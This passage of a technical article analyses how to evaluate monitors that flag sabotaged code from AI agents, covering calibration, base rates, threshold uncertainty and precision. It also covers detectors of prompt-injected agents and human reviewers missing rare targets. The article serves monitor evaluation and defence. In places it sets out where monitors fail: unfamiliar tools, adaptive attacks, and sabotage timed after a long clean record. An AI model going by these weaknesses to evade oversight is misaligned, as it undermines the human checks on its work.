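The best fit for the table above is *a* of about 0.54 and *b* of about −0.27, which turns scores of 0.1, 0.5 and 0.9 into roughly 0.19, 0.43 and 0.71. Temperature scaling is a simpler version that sets *b* to zero and fits only *a*, so it can make scores more or less extreme but can't shift them all in one direction.

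Isotonic regression assumes only that the chance of sabotage never falls as the score rises. It starts with the observed share of sabotage at each score and merges neighbouring scores whose shares are in the wrong order. If four equally large groups had shares of 10%, 30%, 20% and 70%, it would merge the middle two and give both 25%. The method is flexible but needs more data than Platt scaling, and each merge creates ties, which leave fewer thresholds to choose from.

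Apart from such ties, none of these repairs improves the ranking. *Quantiles, Not Points* (Subasic, Rabinovich and Chen, 2026) compared 17 ways of adjusting language models' ratings to match human ones. Fourteen brought the two significantly closer, but their median rank correlation was 0.494 both before and after adjustment.

Wang and colleagues object that Platt scaling and isotonic regression achieve low calibration error by squeezing nearly all scores towards the base rate, so they prefer temperature scaling. Their own results only partly support this. For the stated confidence of Qwen2.5-7B, Platt scaling cut the calibration error from 0.441 to 0.033 and the Brier score from 0.420 to 0.215. With temperature scaling, the Brier score was 0.251, about the same as always guessing 50%. A score that contains little information should translate to a probability close to the base rate, so the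 squeezing is probably due more to a weak rater than to a flaw in the calibration method.

### Correcting for the real base rate

Even a perfectly calibrated probability is correct only at the test set's base rate of sabotage. Testers often sabotage half of the diffs, because a test set with one sabotaged diff in 10,000 would have to be enormous to include enough sabotage. If sabotage is much rarer in real use, the same score corresponds to a much lower probability of sabotage.

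The correction follows from Bayes' rule in its odds form. The odds that a diff with score *s* is sabotage equal the prior odds times how much more common that score is among sabotaged diffs than among benign ones:

test odds = likelihood ratio × old prior odds

real odds = likelihood ratio × new prior odds

If the sabotaged diffs in real use resemble those in the test, and the benign ones do too, the likelihood ratio is the same in both lines. Dividing one line by the other removes it:

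real odds = test odds × (new prior odds / old prior odds)

In a test set that is half sabotage, the prior odds of sabotage are 1, and a calibrated score of 0.99 means odds of 0.99/0.01 = 99. If one diff in 10,000 is sabotaged in real use, the prior odds there are 1 to 9,999. The odds that a diff with this score is sabotaged are then 99/9,999, or about 0.0099, which is a probability of about 1%.

| Calibrated score on a half-sabotaged test set | Probability when one diff in 10,000 is sabotaged |
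|---|---|
| 0.5 | 0.01% |
| 0.9 | 0.09% |
| 0.99 | 1% |
| 0.999 | 9% |
| 0.9999 | 50% |

A diff would need a calibrated score of 0.9999 to have an even chance of being sabotage. A test set of ordinary size is too small to check that score, because only one in 10,000 diffs with it would be benign, and telling 0.9999 from 0.999 would take several thousand such diffs.

The correction multiplies the odds by a constant, which adds a constant to the log-odds (here −9.2), so it is the same as changing *b* in Platt scaling. It changes the probability attached to each diff but not the order of the diffs, and the catch rate and false-positive rate at a given cut stay the same.

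People's judgements need the same correction. In *Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research* (2026), auditors spent 90 minutes on each record of a research project, then estimated the probability that the project was sabotaged. Their median estimate was 54% for sabotaged projects and 40% for benign ones, and the AUROC was 0.59. If 1% of projects were sabotaged, only about 1.6% of the audits with an estimate of 50% or more would involve sabotage, which is hardly better than picking projects at random.

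The formula fails if more than the base rate has changed. Afrin and Shihab tested a related method that estimates the new base rate from unlabelled scores. In simulations where only the base rate changed, it improved the Brier score from 0.233 to 0.214. When they moved to a genuinely different task, the adjusted scores were worse than the raw ones in 49% of cases. A company that moves a monitor from web development to operating system code changes both the diffs and the base rate, so the corrected probability could be far off.

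### How uncertain a threshold is

A threshold is less fragile than a calibrated score because it doesn't require probabilities. The tester can score a set of benign diffs and choose the threshold that flags the target share of them. With 500 benign diffs and a target of 1%, the monitor would flag anything at or above the fifth-highest score. But those five diffs are a small sample, and another 500 would have given a different threshold.

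Gao (2026), in *From Probe Scores to Alarm Policies*, a study of monitors that read an agent's internal activations, uses a standard result that gives the size of this uncertainty. If the benign diffs are independent and no scores are tied, the true false-positive rate of a threshold at the *r*-th highest of *m* benign scores follows a beta distribution:

true false-positive rate ~ Beta(*r*, *m* − *r* + 1)

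If the threshold is set at the fifth-highest score among 500 benign diffs, the true false-positive rate follows a Beta(5, 496) distribution, whatever the shape of the score distribution. This has a mean of 1.0% and a 95% interval from 0.3% to 2.0%. Two teams could therefore follow the same procedure with the same monitor, both report a 1% false-positive rate, and have true rates that differ sixfold. With 5,000 benign diffs and a threshold at the fiftieth-highest score, the interval narrows to about 0.7% to 1.3%.

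| Threshold set at | Average true rate | 95% interval | 95% sure to be below |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5th-highest of 500 | 1.0% | 0.3%–2.0% | 1.8% |
| 2nd-highest of 500 | 0.4% | 0.05%–1.1% | 0.95% |
| 50th-highest of 5,000 | 1.0% | 0.7%–1.3% | 1.2% |

A team that must stay below 1% can choose a stricter threshold to allow for this. With 500 benign diffs, it would use the second-highest score, which keeps the true rate below 1% with 95% confidence but also catches less sabotage. With fewer than 299 benign diffs, even the highest score is not a strict enough threshold for that confidence level. In such cases, Gao sets no threshold. One of his four datasets had only 23 independent benign cases for this purpose, too few even for a 10% limit, and he did not count the resulting zero alarms as a success.

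If 30 benign diffs tie for the fifth-highest score, flagging everything at that score breaks the bound. Gao flags only diffs that score strictly higher, which keeps the bound valid but may flag fewer diffs than intended.

A small change in the threshold can greatly change the catch rate. In *Beyond AUROC*, Tehabsim, Al-Housani and colleagues (2026) tested detectors for jailbreaks, which are prompts that try to get a chatbot to break its rules. For one detector and one family of attack prompts, the catch rate rose from 11% to 100% as the false-positive rate rose from 5.4% to 7.6%. A tester who saw these results before choosing the threshold would be strongly tempted to allow 7.6%, and could then publish a 100% catch rate.

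The threshold has to come from different diffs than the ones in the test. If a tester sets it to flag 1% of the test's own benign diffs, the measured false-positive rate will be 1% by construction and gives no evidence about new code. If the tester also uses the test's sabotaged diffs to choose the threshold, the measured catch rate will be too high. A careful tester uses one set of diffs to fit any calibration, a second to set the threshold, and a third to measure the result, and looks at the third set only once.

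Overlap is easy to miss. Gao found that 207 of the 969 distinct requests in one published test set also appeared in its training set. Shared labels can also inflate a result. Afrin and Shihab found a correlation of 0.25 between the difference in accuracy on two tasks and how well a calibration transferred, with a confidence interval that included zero. If they had used the same labels to measure both, the correlation would have been 0.44.

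### Summaries for the low-false-alarm region

Teams that can tolerate very few false alarms use only the far left end of the ROC curve, but AUROC averages over the whole curve. In this invented comparison, the monitor with the higher AUROC is much worse for these teams.

| | Monitor A | Monitor B |
|---|---|---|
| Catch rate at false-positive rates of 0–1% | 60% | 10% |
| Catch rate at 1–10% | 70% | 60% |
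| Catch rate at 10–100% | 90% | 99% |
| AUROC | 0.88 | 0.95 |
| Partial AUROC, 0–5% | 0.68 | 0.50 |
| Log-AUROC, 0.1–100% | 0.73 | 0.56 |

Monitor B's lead comes from false-positive rates above 10%, which make up nine tenths of the horizontal axis but are too high for any reviewer to tolerate.

Partial AUROC measures only the area up to a chosen limit. *Robust Detection of LLM-Generated Text under Contamination* (2026), which tests detectors of machine-written text, takes the area between 0% and 5% and divides it by 0.05, which gives the average catch rate over that range. Stemma also stops at 5% but rescales the area so that random guessing gets 0.5 and a perfect score is still 1. With this rescaling, Monitor A would get 0.84 instead of 0.68, so a partial AUROC is hard to interpret without its formula.

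Log-AUROC keeps a wider range but plots the false-positive rate on a logarithmic scale, so each tenfold step counts equally. Between limits *l* and *h*, it is

log-AUROC = (1 / ln(*h*/*l*)) ∫ catch rate(*u*) d*u*/*u*

where *u* is the false-positive rate and runs from *l* to *h*. In the table, the three steps from 0.1% to 100% each count for a third. The scale can't start at zero, and the starting point should be no lower than the benign set can support. With 1,000 benign diffs, the catch rate at 0.1% depends on where a single benign diff happens to score.

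Real detectors can also have a high AUROC but catch few attacks when the false positive rate must be low. The highest average AUROC that Tehabsim and colleagues measured was 0.962. That detector caught 74% of attack prompts when its threshold was set for 5% false positives, but 17% when it was set for 1%.

Gao trained a monitor directly for partial AUROC, on the task of predicting whether a model would refuse a request. AUROC fell from 0.934 to 0.918, but at a 10% false positive limit the catch rate rose from 78% to 81%, with fewer false alarms. The same approach did worse at a 5% limit, where the catch rate fell from 72% to 57%. Gao had seen the test results beforehand and calls the experiment exploratory. It is good evidence that the two measures can disagree, but not that training on partial AUROC is generally better. A report should give the catch rate at the threshold the team plans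 to use, because a summary over a range of thresholds can hide a bad result at one of them.

### Whether a calibration carries over to another task

Afrin and Shihab ran the most direct test of this. They had language models judge whether answers were correct in eight kinds of task, including maths, summarisation and code generation, and give a probability each time. They then fitted a calibration on one task, applied it to another, and counted the transfer as harmful if the Brier score was worse than with no calibration.

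| Calibration | Harmful transfers |
|---|---|
| Platt scaling fitted on another task | 34% |
| Temperature scaling fitted on another task | 13% |
| Temperature scaling fitted on 16 examples from the new task | 9% |

These results come from eight small judges. With four stronger judges, Platt scaling fitted on another task did harm in 55% of transfers, apparently because their raw probabilities were already better. Claude Sonnet 4.5, the only frontier model in the study, showed the same tendency. Each task had only 40 items, so the results for individual transfers are noisy, but the advantage of using examples from the new task remained when another model wrote the answers.

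Subasic and colleagues reached a similar conclusion with ratings instead of probabilities. How well calibration worked depended more on the dataset than on the method, the judge or the amount of labelled data. On one dataset that mixed many tasks, each with its own instructions, no method came close to its usual accuracy. They recommend calibrating separately for each task, which takes little extra work because the judge itself stays the same.

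This advice is harder to follow for sabotage because sixteen diffs from real use would almost certainly all be benign, and fitting a probability of sabotage requires examples of sabotage. A team would have to plant some, and the probabilities would then depend on how realistic the planted sabotage was. Resetting a threshold is much easier because it requires only benign diffs from the new task.

A threshold has to be set again when the inputs change. Tehabsim and colleagues set thresholds for 5% false positives on curated prompts, then applied them to prompts from real users. One detector's false-positive rate rose to between 11.6% and 27.2%, depending on the chatbot. The curated threshold also made the catch rate look better. On Llama-2, the detector caught 96.5% of attack prompts at that threshold, but only 57% when the threshold was reset on real prompts to bring false positives back to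 near 5%. In a test with hijacked agents, Gao found that a threshold's false-positive rate roughly doubled on new cases.

A threshold that raises no false alarms on old data can still raise many on new data. In *Safe Resemblance, Silent Propagation* (2026), a study of guardrails that compare the text of agents' replies, a threshold raised no alarms on 192 legitimate replies from each of two models. By the rule of three, the false-positive rate should be below about 1.6%. But on legitimate replies to new kinds of request, in new formats, it flagged 7.8% for one model and 35.9% for the other.

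*Fine-Grained Uncertainty Quantification for Long-Form Language Model Outputs* (2026) reports that thresholds for spotting unreliable claims worked nearly as well on a second dataset, with a loss of at most 0.028, when the scoring method stayed the same, but transferred badly between scoring methods. Those thresholds were chosen to maximize F1, a measure that balances precision and recall and often changes little near its peak. A threshold for 1% false positives instead depends on the few highest benign scores, which are probably the first to change when the code does.

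Replacing the model behind a monitor changes how it scores, even if the instructions stay the same. In *LLM Judges as Raters* (2026), essay scores fell by 133 points, or 0.74 of a standard deviation of the human scores, when the judge went from Sonnet 4.5 to 4.6. Adjusting the new version on 100 essays removed the shift on average, with an error of about 13 points either way. For a sabotage monitor, the highest benign scores must also be right, which is harder than correcting an average shift because 100 benign diffs contain only about one from the top 1%.

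## How rare sabotage changes what an alert means

A monitor can catch 90% of sabotaged diffs and flag only 1% of benign ones, yet more than 99% of its alerts can still be false alarms. This happens when sabotage is so rare that 1% of the benign diffs is far more than 90% of the sabotaged ones.

### Calculating precision

Let π be the base rate, TPR the catch rate and FPR the false-positive rate. Among *N* diffs, π*N* are sabotaged, and the monitor flags π*N* × TPR of them. The other (1 − π)*N* are benign, and it flags (1 − π)*N* × FPR of those. Precision is the first number of flags divided by the total, and *N* cancels out:

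precision = π × TPR / (π × TPR + (1 − π) × FPR)

Suppose a company's agents write 100,000 diffs, ten of them sabotaged, and the monitor catches nine of the ten. These numbers are invented.

| False-positive rate | Real alerts | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 9 | about 1,000 | 0.9% |
| 0.2% | 9 | about 200 | 4.3% |
| 0.009% | 9 | about 9 | 50% |

Improving the catch rate barely raises precision. If the monitor in the top row caught all ten, its precision would rise only from 0.9% to 1.0%. Cutting its false-positive rate to a fifth would raise precision almost fivefold, but very low false-positive rates are hard to demonstrate. By the rule of three, a tester would need about 33,000 independent benign diffs without an alarm to show a rate below 0.009%.

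Counting sessions instead of diffs makes sabotage look more common but doesn't make alerts much more reliable. If the 100,000 diffs come from 2,000 sessions of 50 and the ten sabotaged diffs are all in different sessions, the base rate is 0.5% per session, fifty times higher than per diff. But with a false alarm rate of 0.2% per diff, 9.5% of harmless sessions have a false alarm, as calculated earlier, so a reviewer still gets about 190 false alerts for nine real ones.

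The share of unflagged diffs that are clean makes the monitor look much better. In the top row, the monitor passes about 99,000 diffs and only one of them is sabotaged, so 99.999% of what it passes is clean, compared with 99.99% if there were no monitor.

### Axelsson's argument about intrusion detection

In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson applied the same formula to software that searches computer logs for break-ins. He imagined a site with a few dozen computers that together write 1,000,000 log records a day. He assumed two attempted intrusions a day, each affecting ten records, so 20 of the 1,000,000 records, or 2 in 100,000, are part of an intrusion.

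With a perfect catch rate and a false-positive rate of 1 in 100,000, about 66% of alarms would be real. Lowering the catch rate to 70% would only reduce this to 58%. But if the false-positive rate rose to 1 in 1,000, about 2% of alarms would be real even with a perfect catch rate. Axelsson concluded that intrusion detection systems are limited by how well they suppress false alarms rather than how well they recognise intrusions. Several detectors whose published results he compared had false-positive rates ten to a thousand times too high for his scenario.

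He chose the intrusion rate himself and treated all intrusions as equally hard to detect. He had no experiments on how many false alarms a security officer would tolerate, so he relied on studies of operators at power stations, paper mills and similar plants. These suggested that most operators would lose faith in a device well before half its alarms were false.

Axelsson expected the problem to get worse, because computers would produce more log data while intrusions would not increase as fast. This may not apply to coding agents. If every diff has the same small chance of being sabotaged, sabotage will grow in proportion to the number of diffs and the base rate will stay the same.

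Erbacher (2022), in *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity*, calculated how many analysts a site would need to handle typical false-positive rates. At a large site with 2.5 terabytes of incoming traffic a day, a detector that wrongly flagged 0.37% of network packets would raise about 443,000 false alarms an hour. An analyst can check about 12 alerts an hour, so the site would need about 37,000 analysts on every shift. Counting individual packets makes the total extreme, and Erbacher acknowledges that the problem is smaller for whole sessions. At the same pace, one analyst would need 83 hours to check the 1,000 false alarms in the invented example, and probably more, because a code diff probably takes longer than five minutes to check.

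Erbacher also found that papers use "false alarm rate" for several different quantities. Some divide false alarms by the number of benign items, at least one divides them by the number of alerts, and others use the share of attacks the detector missed. In the top row of the table above, these definitions give 1%, 99% and 10%.

### Detectors of hijacked agents at a 2% attack rate

In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) measured the effect on detectors that read records of what AI agents did. The attacks were prompt injections, in which an outsider plants instructions in an email, web page or other material that the agent reads. These attacks resemble code sabotage, but the harmful goal comes from outside the agent and few of the tasks involve writing code.

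They first checked eleven published evaluations of such detectors. In the test sets that mixed the two classes, attacks or other anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the samples, and no evaluation varied that share. Readers of those papers would struggle to tell how many alerts would be false in real use.

Abbasi and colleagues then tested several detectors on AgentDrift, a set of synthetic agent records generated by a Llama model. The test pool had 831 attacked records, 600 ordinary benign ones and 225 hard negatives. For the detectors they trained, they set each threshold to flag 80% of the attacks in the training data, then calculated what the precision would be if 2% of records contained an attack. The last two rows show AlignmentCheck, a monitor released by Meta, which uses its own decision rule.

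| Detector | AUROC | Attacks flagged | Benign records flagged | Precision at a 2% attack rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Logistic regression on tools used and behaviour | 0.879 | 77.1% | 19.2% | 7.6% |
| Small neural network reading tool calls in order | 0.936 | 68.2% | 4.5% | 23.8% |
| Word-frequency model | 0.999 | 76.3% | 0% | 100% |
| AlignmentCheck with Llama 3.3 70B | 0.856 | 84.7% | 22.1% | 7.3% |
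| AlignmentCheck with Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0.817 | 87.4% | 31.3% | 5.4% |

The logistic regression would raise about 12 false alerts for every real one, despite its AUROC of 0.879. If the attack rate were 0.1%, only 0.4% of its alerts would be real.

The logistic regression's precision also depended heavily on which benign records were in the pool. It flagged 11.8% of ordinary benign records and 38.7% of hard negatives. At the same 2% attack rate, its precision would be 11.7% with only ordinary records, 7.6% with the actual mix and 3.9% with only hard negatives. Halving the attack rate to 1% with the actual mix would also lower precision to 3.9%. A precision figure is therefore hard to interpret without both the attack rate and a description of the benign records.

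The word-frequency model's perfect precision is almost certainly an artefact. Each category of record in AgentDrift came from its own template, so the model could tell the categories apart by their wording. For example, the token "2026" appeared in 74% of the benign training records but only 5% of the attacked ones. When Abbasi and colleagues tested the model on AgentDojo, a benchmark with records of real agent runs, its AUROC was 0.52, about the same as guessing.

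AlignmentCheck did much better on AgentDojo. It shows a language model the user's request and the agent's actions so far, asks it whether the latest action serves a goal the user didn't set, and flags the whole record if any step looks wrong. The AUROC was 0.930 with Llama and 0.934 with Claude, so the two are almost equal by that measure.

The alerts would be very different, however. The Llama version flagged 90.0% of compromised runs and 17.3% of benign ones, so at a 2% attack rate only 9.6% of its alerts would be for compromised runs. The Claude version flagged 88.3% and 3.8%, which raises that share, the precision, to 32%. The 32% is uncertain because only about 15 of the 392 benign runs were flagged, and its 95% interval is 20% to 59%. The order was reversed on AgentDrift, as the table shows, so neither version is consistently better. Meta had also evaluated the prompt on AgentDojo,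 which may have inflated both versions' results there.

Thresholds also failed when agents used unfamiliar tools. Abbasi and colleagues trained detectors on four kinds of work, such as email and banking, and tested them on a fifth with entirely different tools. The logistic regression's false-positive rate rose to between 50% and 72%, from between 12% and 32% when its training had included the same kinds of work. In a separate test, hiding only the tool names raised the small neural network's false-positive rate from 4.5% to 73.7%. At a 2% attack rate, its precision would then have been at most 2.7% even if it had caught every attack, compared with 2% for flagging records at random.

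Randomly hiding tool names during training was an easy fix for part of this, and it kept the network's false-positive rate between 5% and 7%. But another detector could interpret new tool names from their text, and its false-positive rate still rose from 0.1% to 10.6% on unfamiliar web tasks. On banking tasks, its catch rate fell to 34.5% instead. A new kind of work can therefore cause many more false alarms or fewer catches, and a team can't tell in advance which it will get.

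All of these rates come from attacks that didn't adapt to the detector. An adaptive attacker could lower the catch rate, which would also lower the precision, so the results are probably optimistic in that respect.

### Reweighting a test set with too much sabotage

The base rate of sabotage affects precision but not the catch rate or the false-positive rate, as long as the kinds of sabotaged and benign items stay the same. A monitor that reads each diff separately gives it the same score whether or not the other diffs are sabotaged. A test set that is half sabotage can therefore be used to measure the catch rate and false-positive rate, but its precision isn't the precision a team will see.

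To correct it, the tester gives each item a weight. If a share *p* of the test items are sabotaged and the real base rate is π, the weights are

sabotaged item: π / *p*

benign item: (1 − π) / (1 − *p*)

Suppose a tester uses 500 sabotaged and 500 benign diffs (numbers again invented), and the monitor flags 450 of the sabotaged diffs and 5 of the benign ones. Its precision on the test is 450/455, or 99%. If one diff in 10,000 is sabotaged in real use, each sabotaged diff gets a weight of 0.0002 and each benign one a weight of about 2. The weighted flags are then 450 × 0.0002 = 0.09 and 5 × 2 = 10, so the precision is 0.09/10.09, or 0.9%, as in the top row of the first table.

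The precision estimate also becomes more uncertain when sabotage is rare. Five alarms on 500 benign diffs are compatible with a true false-positive rate from about 0.3% to 2.3%, so the real precision could be from about 0.4% to 2.7%. Uncertainty in the catch rate has little effect by comparison, so a tester who wants a better precision estimate should collect more benign diffs rather than more sabotage.

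Discarding sabotaged items until the test set has a realistic base rate is a worse solution than weighting. An earlier version of the study by Abbasi and colleagues did this, and its interval for a precision-based summary of the logistic regression was about 2.5 times as wide as the interval from weighting.

That summary averages the precision over all thresholds, at a stated base rate:

weighted average precision = Σ (TPR at threshold *k* − TPR at threshold *k* − 1) × precision at threshold *k*

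where the thresholds run from strictest to loosest. It can reverse a ranking by AUROC. On AgentDrift, AlignmentCheck with Llama had an AUROC of 0.856, slightly above the 0.830 of a logistic regression that used only behaviour such as the number of tool calls. At a 2% attack rate, its weighted average precision was 0.089, compared with 0.152 for the logistic regression. A random scorer gets about 0.02.

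The same weighting works for different kinds of benign diffs. If 5% of a team's benign diffs were hard negatives, the logistic regression in the large table would have a false-positive rate of 0.95 × 11.8% + 0.05 × 38.7%, or about 13.1%. Its precision at a 2% attack rate would then be 10.7% instead of 7.6%.

Catch rates also need this correction when the mix of sabotage changes. A hypothetical monitor that catches 95% of crude sabotage and 40% of subtle sabotage would catch 84% of all cases if 80% of them were crude, but 51% if 20% were. Reweighting the results can't correct for kinds of sabotage that the test left out.

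### Choosing a threshold by cost

Once a team has a base rate, it can weigh the cost of reviewing alerts against the cost of missing sabotage. Let *R* be the cost of reviewing one diff and *M* the cost of one missed sabotage, and assume for now that a review always finds the sabotage. Leaving a diff unread costs *M* times the probability *P* that it is sabotaged, so a review is worthwhile when

*P* > *R* / *M*

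The same rule works without individual probabilities. Lowering the threshold catches more sabotage, and each extra catch saves *M* − *R*. It also raises more false alarms, and each costs *R*. The lower threshold pays off when

increase in TPR / increase in FPR > ((1 − π) / π) × *R* / (*M* − *R*)

The next table shows three thresholds for an invented monitor, again with ten sabotaged diffs in 100,000. The last column compares each row with the one above it, and the first row with flagging nothing.

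| Catch rate | False-positive rate | Sabotage caught | False alarms | Precision | Extra false alarms per extra catch |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 0.05% | 5 | 50 | 9.1% | 10 |
| 70% | 0.2% | 7 | 200 | 3.4% | 75 |
| 90% | 1% | 9 | 1,000 | 0.9% | 400 |

If a review costs $50, catching each extra sabotage costs about $500 in the first row, $3,750 in the second and $20,000 in the third. A team that expects a missed sabotage to cost $10,000 should choose the middle threshold.

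With realistic damages, the rule can call for reading every diff. Erbacher uses $3.92 million as the average cost of a successful attack. If a review costs $50, a diff is then worth reading when its chance of being sabotaged is above 0.0013%. The average diff in this example has a 0.01% chance, so the team should read all 100,000. That would cost $5 million and prevent an expected $39 million in damage.

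But if the base rate were one in a million, the expected damage would be only $392,000, and reading everything would cost far more than it saved. Whether to read everything therefore depends on a base rate that nobody knows to within a factor of a hundred, and on how good the reviewers are. If they recognise only a share *q* of the sabotage they read, the minimum probability rises to *R* / (*qM*).

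### A base rate the saboteur can change

Axelsson's intrusion rate was a guess, but a company could in principle replace it with a count of past intrusions. Counting is less useful for a deliberate saboteur, because the saboteur decides how often to act. An agent could write 100,000 harmless diffs and sabotage the next one. After those 100,000 diffs, the rule of three would give an upper bound of 0.003% on the base rate, but the bound is valid only if the chance of sabotage stays constant and someone would have noticed any sabotage that occurred.

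Many agents in a company may also be copies of one model. If something leads one copy to sabotage its work, the same cause could affect the others, and sabotage might go from absent to common within a day.

Precision depends on the base rate, so it is better to calculate it for a range of base rates than for one. A monitor with a 90% catch rate and a 1% false-positive rate has a precision of 48% if one diff in 100 is sabotaged, 8% at one in 1,000, 0.9% at one in 10,000 and 0.09% at one in 100,000.

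The number of alerts is much easier to predict. For 100,000 diffs, this monitor raises about 1,000 alerts if there is no sabotage and about 1,090 if one diff in 1,000 is sabotaged. A team can therefore choose a threshold that fits its review budget without knowing the base rate. If an agent sabotages only one diff, the monitor has a 10% chance of missing it, regardless of its precision on earlier days.

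### Precision or catches within a review budget

Axelsson considered precision most important. He thought that if most alarms were false, a security officer would quickly learn to ignore the system, even if there were few enough alarms to investigate every one. On this view, a monitor with a precision of 0.9% is close to useless, however much sabotage it flags.

On the opposing view, low precision is acceptable because sabotage is rare and missing it can be very expensive. If one backdoor could do millions of dollars of damage, reading 1,009 diffs to find nine is worth the money, and a monitor should be judged by how much of the sabotage reaches a reviewer within the budget. Erbacher partly supports this view, noting that correctly passing a harmless item has no value in security, while a missed attack can be very expensive. But he also thinks that false positives need to fall a great deal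 before such detectors are viable.

Catch rate and precision always rank monitors in the same order when the review budget is fixed, because both divide the number of sabotaged diffs caught by a constant. Suppose a team can read 200 of 100,000 diffs, ten of the 100,000 are sabotaged, and each monitor sends its 200 highest-scoring diffs. A monitor that catches eight has a catch rate of 80% and a precision of 4%, while one that catches five has a catch rate of 50% and a precision of 2.5%.

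The disagreement is about how large the budget should be and whether reviewers keep paying attention when nearly every alert is false. The cost rule helps answer the first question, but the second depends on human behavior, and Axelsson had little evidence on it.

### People miss more when targets are rare

Psychologists have studied a similar problem in visual search, where people look for a target such as a weapon in luggage or a tumour in an X-ray. Wolfe, Horowitz and Kenner (2005), in *Rare targets are often missed in visual search*, reported that participants missed 7% of targets when half the images contained one and 30% when only 1% did. Researchers call this tendency to miss a larger share of targets when they are rare the low-prevalence effect.

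In *Rare Targets Are Rarely Missed in Correctable Search* (2007), Fleck and Mitroff argued that people often see the rare target but have already pressed the wrong key out of habit. They asked 20 people to find a tool among pictures of other objects and let half of them correct their previous answer.

| Share of images with a target | Missed, no corrections allowed | Missed, corrections allowed |
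|---|---|---|
| 50% | 10% | 4% |
| 10% | 19% | 10% |
| 2% | 31% | 10% |

Letting people correct their responses clearly helped. Fleck and Mitroff concluded that prevalence has no effect when searchers can do this, but ten people is a small sample for such a strong conclusion, and their misses still rose from 4% to 10%. The average response also took less than three seconds, so slips of the finger are probably a much smaller part of the problem in code review.

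They doubted that the effect explained missed tumours, because radiologists work far more slowly. Evans, Birdwell and Wolfe (2013) tested this in a hospital in *If You Don't Find It Often, You Often Don't Find It*. Over nine months they slipped 50 mammograms with cancer and 50 without into the normal work of 14 radiologists, slowly enough that only about 1% of the cases contained cancer. Later, six of the radiologists read all 100 in one session. They missed 12% of the cancers, compared with the 30% that the full group had missed in the clinic. All six found seven of the 15 cancers missed in the clinic.

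This is the closest of these experiments to code review, since trained people were doing their real job at their normal pace. But the two conditions differed in setting as well as prevalence, as one was a clinic and the other a laboratory where everyone knew it was a test. Evans and colleagues acknowledge this, but argue that motivation should have been higher in the clinic, which would have made the effect they found smaller.

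Not every study finds the effect. *Visual Search of Experts in Medical Image Reading*, also from 2013, reports no increase in misses for rare targets, even among novices, and suggests that the task may have been too easy. The Association for Psychological Science's *Super Rare Items Are Most Likely to Be Missed* describes a large effect in a study by Mitroff and Biggs of people playing a luggage-screening game. Players spotted 92% of items that appeared more than 1% of the time but only 27% of those that appeared less than 0.15% of the time.

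*The role of feedback in the low-prevalence effect* (Caruso, Fox and colleagues, 2026), a meta-analysis of 62 comparisons from 29 publications, is the best summary of the evidence. When targets were rare, people needed more evidence before they reported one, and the average effect was very large, at 1.8 standard deviations. Their ability to tell targets from other items did not reliably change. In a monitor's terms, people raise their threshold, so they miss more targets but give fewer false alarms.

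The average effect is probably too high an estimate for code review. The effect was larger when participants learned after every trial whether they had been right, and reviewers of real code seldom find out so quickly. Smaller studies also reported larger effects, possibly because of publication bias. However, most low-prevalence conditions had targets in 2% to 5% of trials and few had them in less than 1%, so there is less evidence about the rates that matter most for sabotage.

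Lowering the threshold again is difficult. *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance* describes seven remedies that Wolfe and colleagues tried, including working in pairs and forcing people to slow down. Only short bursts of frequent targets with feedback increased detection, and they also increased false alarms.

If the effect carries over to code, the reweighting above would not work for human reviewers, because their catch rate would depend on the base rate. Reviewers who do well in a test where half the diffs are sabotaged could do noticeably worse at work, where sabotage is rare.

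Precision may also affect how much of the flagged sabotage reviewers catch, because for someone who reads only flagged diffs, the prevalence of sabotage is the monitor's precision. Suppose two monitors each flag nine of ten sabotaged diffs, one with a precision of 0.9% and the other with 50%, and their reviewers miss sabotage at the rates the radiologists had at 1% and 50% prevalence. The reviewers would find about 6.3 of the ten with the first monitor and 7.9 with the second. The radiologists' miss rates are only a stand-in, but they illustrate how false alarms could reduce the amount of sabotage a team stops even when it has time to read every alert.

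## Why the sabotage in a test may be too easy to catch

A high catch rate may mean that the monitor is strong or that the attacks are weak, because the rate depends on both. *It's Just a Small Weapon* (2026) gives an example, though from reward hacking (getting credit for a task by exploiting how it is scored) rather than sabotage. The monitor, Claude Haiku 4.5, could not see the agents' reasoning, and its threshold was set at a 2% false-positive rate. On one set of programming tasks, it caught 86% of the hacks by the model gpt-oss-20b but only 61% of those by a group of models trained to have a particular character. A test with only gpt-oss-20b would have given the monitor a catch rate 25 percentage points higher than a test with only the other group.

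### A lower bound on what gets through

Let *A* be the set of attack policies an attacker could use, and let *m*(*a*) be the monitor's miss rate against policy *a* at a fixed threshold. The miss rate against the best attack is the largest of these:

*m*\* = max *m*(*a*) over all *a* in *A*

A tester can try only a few policies, *a*₁ to *a*ₖ. They all belong to *A*, so none of them can have a higher miss rate than the best attack:

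max(*m*(*a*₁), …, *m*(*a*ₖ)) ≤ *m*\*

A monitor's highest miss rate against the attacks tried is a lower bound on its miss rate against the best attack, and the matching catch rate is an upper bound on its catch rate against that attack. Trying more attacks can only raise the lower bound. The test gives no upper bound on the miss rate, so the tester can't tell how much higher it would be against the best attack.

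Uesato, O'Donoghue and colleagues (2018) argue in *Adversarial Risk and the Dangers of Evaluating Against Weak Attacks* that weak attacks can make image classifiers look safer than they are. They call the difference between the true risk and the measured risk "obscurity", which is large when many successful attacks exist but the tester's attacker fails to find them. Without an estimate of obscurity, they write, high scores could come from "strong defenses or weak attacks". They recommend asking whether the test would have found a weakness if there had been one, because that is easier to reason about than whether a weakness exists.

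A confidence interval for a monitor's miss rate accounts for sampling error, but not for the possibility of a better attack. Suppose a monitor misses 5 of 100 sabotaged diffs (an invented result). The 95% interval for its miss rate against that attack policy is about 1.6% to 11%. The lower end is also a lower bound for the best attack policy, which must get through at least as often as the tested one. The upper end applies only to the tested policy. A better policy might get through 60% of the time, and 10,000 more runs with the old one would narrow the interval without revealing this.

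Sampling error can also push the bound too high. If a tester tries 20 policies that all have a true miss rate of 10%, with 50 runs each, the worst result will typically be about 9 misses in 50, or 18%. The tester should rerun the policy with the most misses on new tasks and report the second result.

### Sabotage written to order

A model instructed to sabotage code may behave differently from one that does so unprompted, which could make its sabotage easier or harder to catch.

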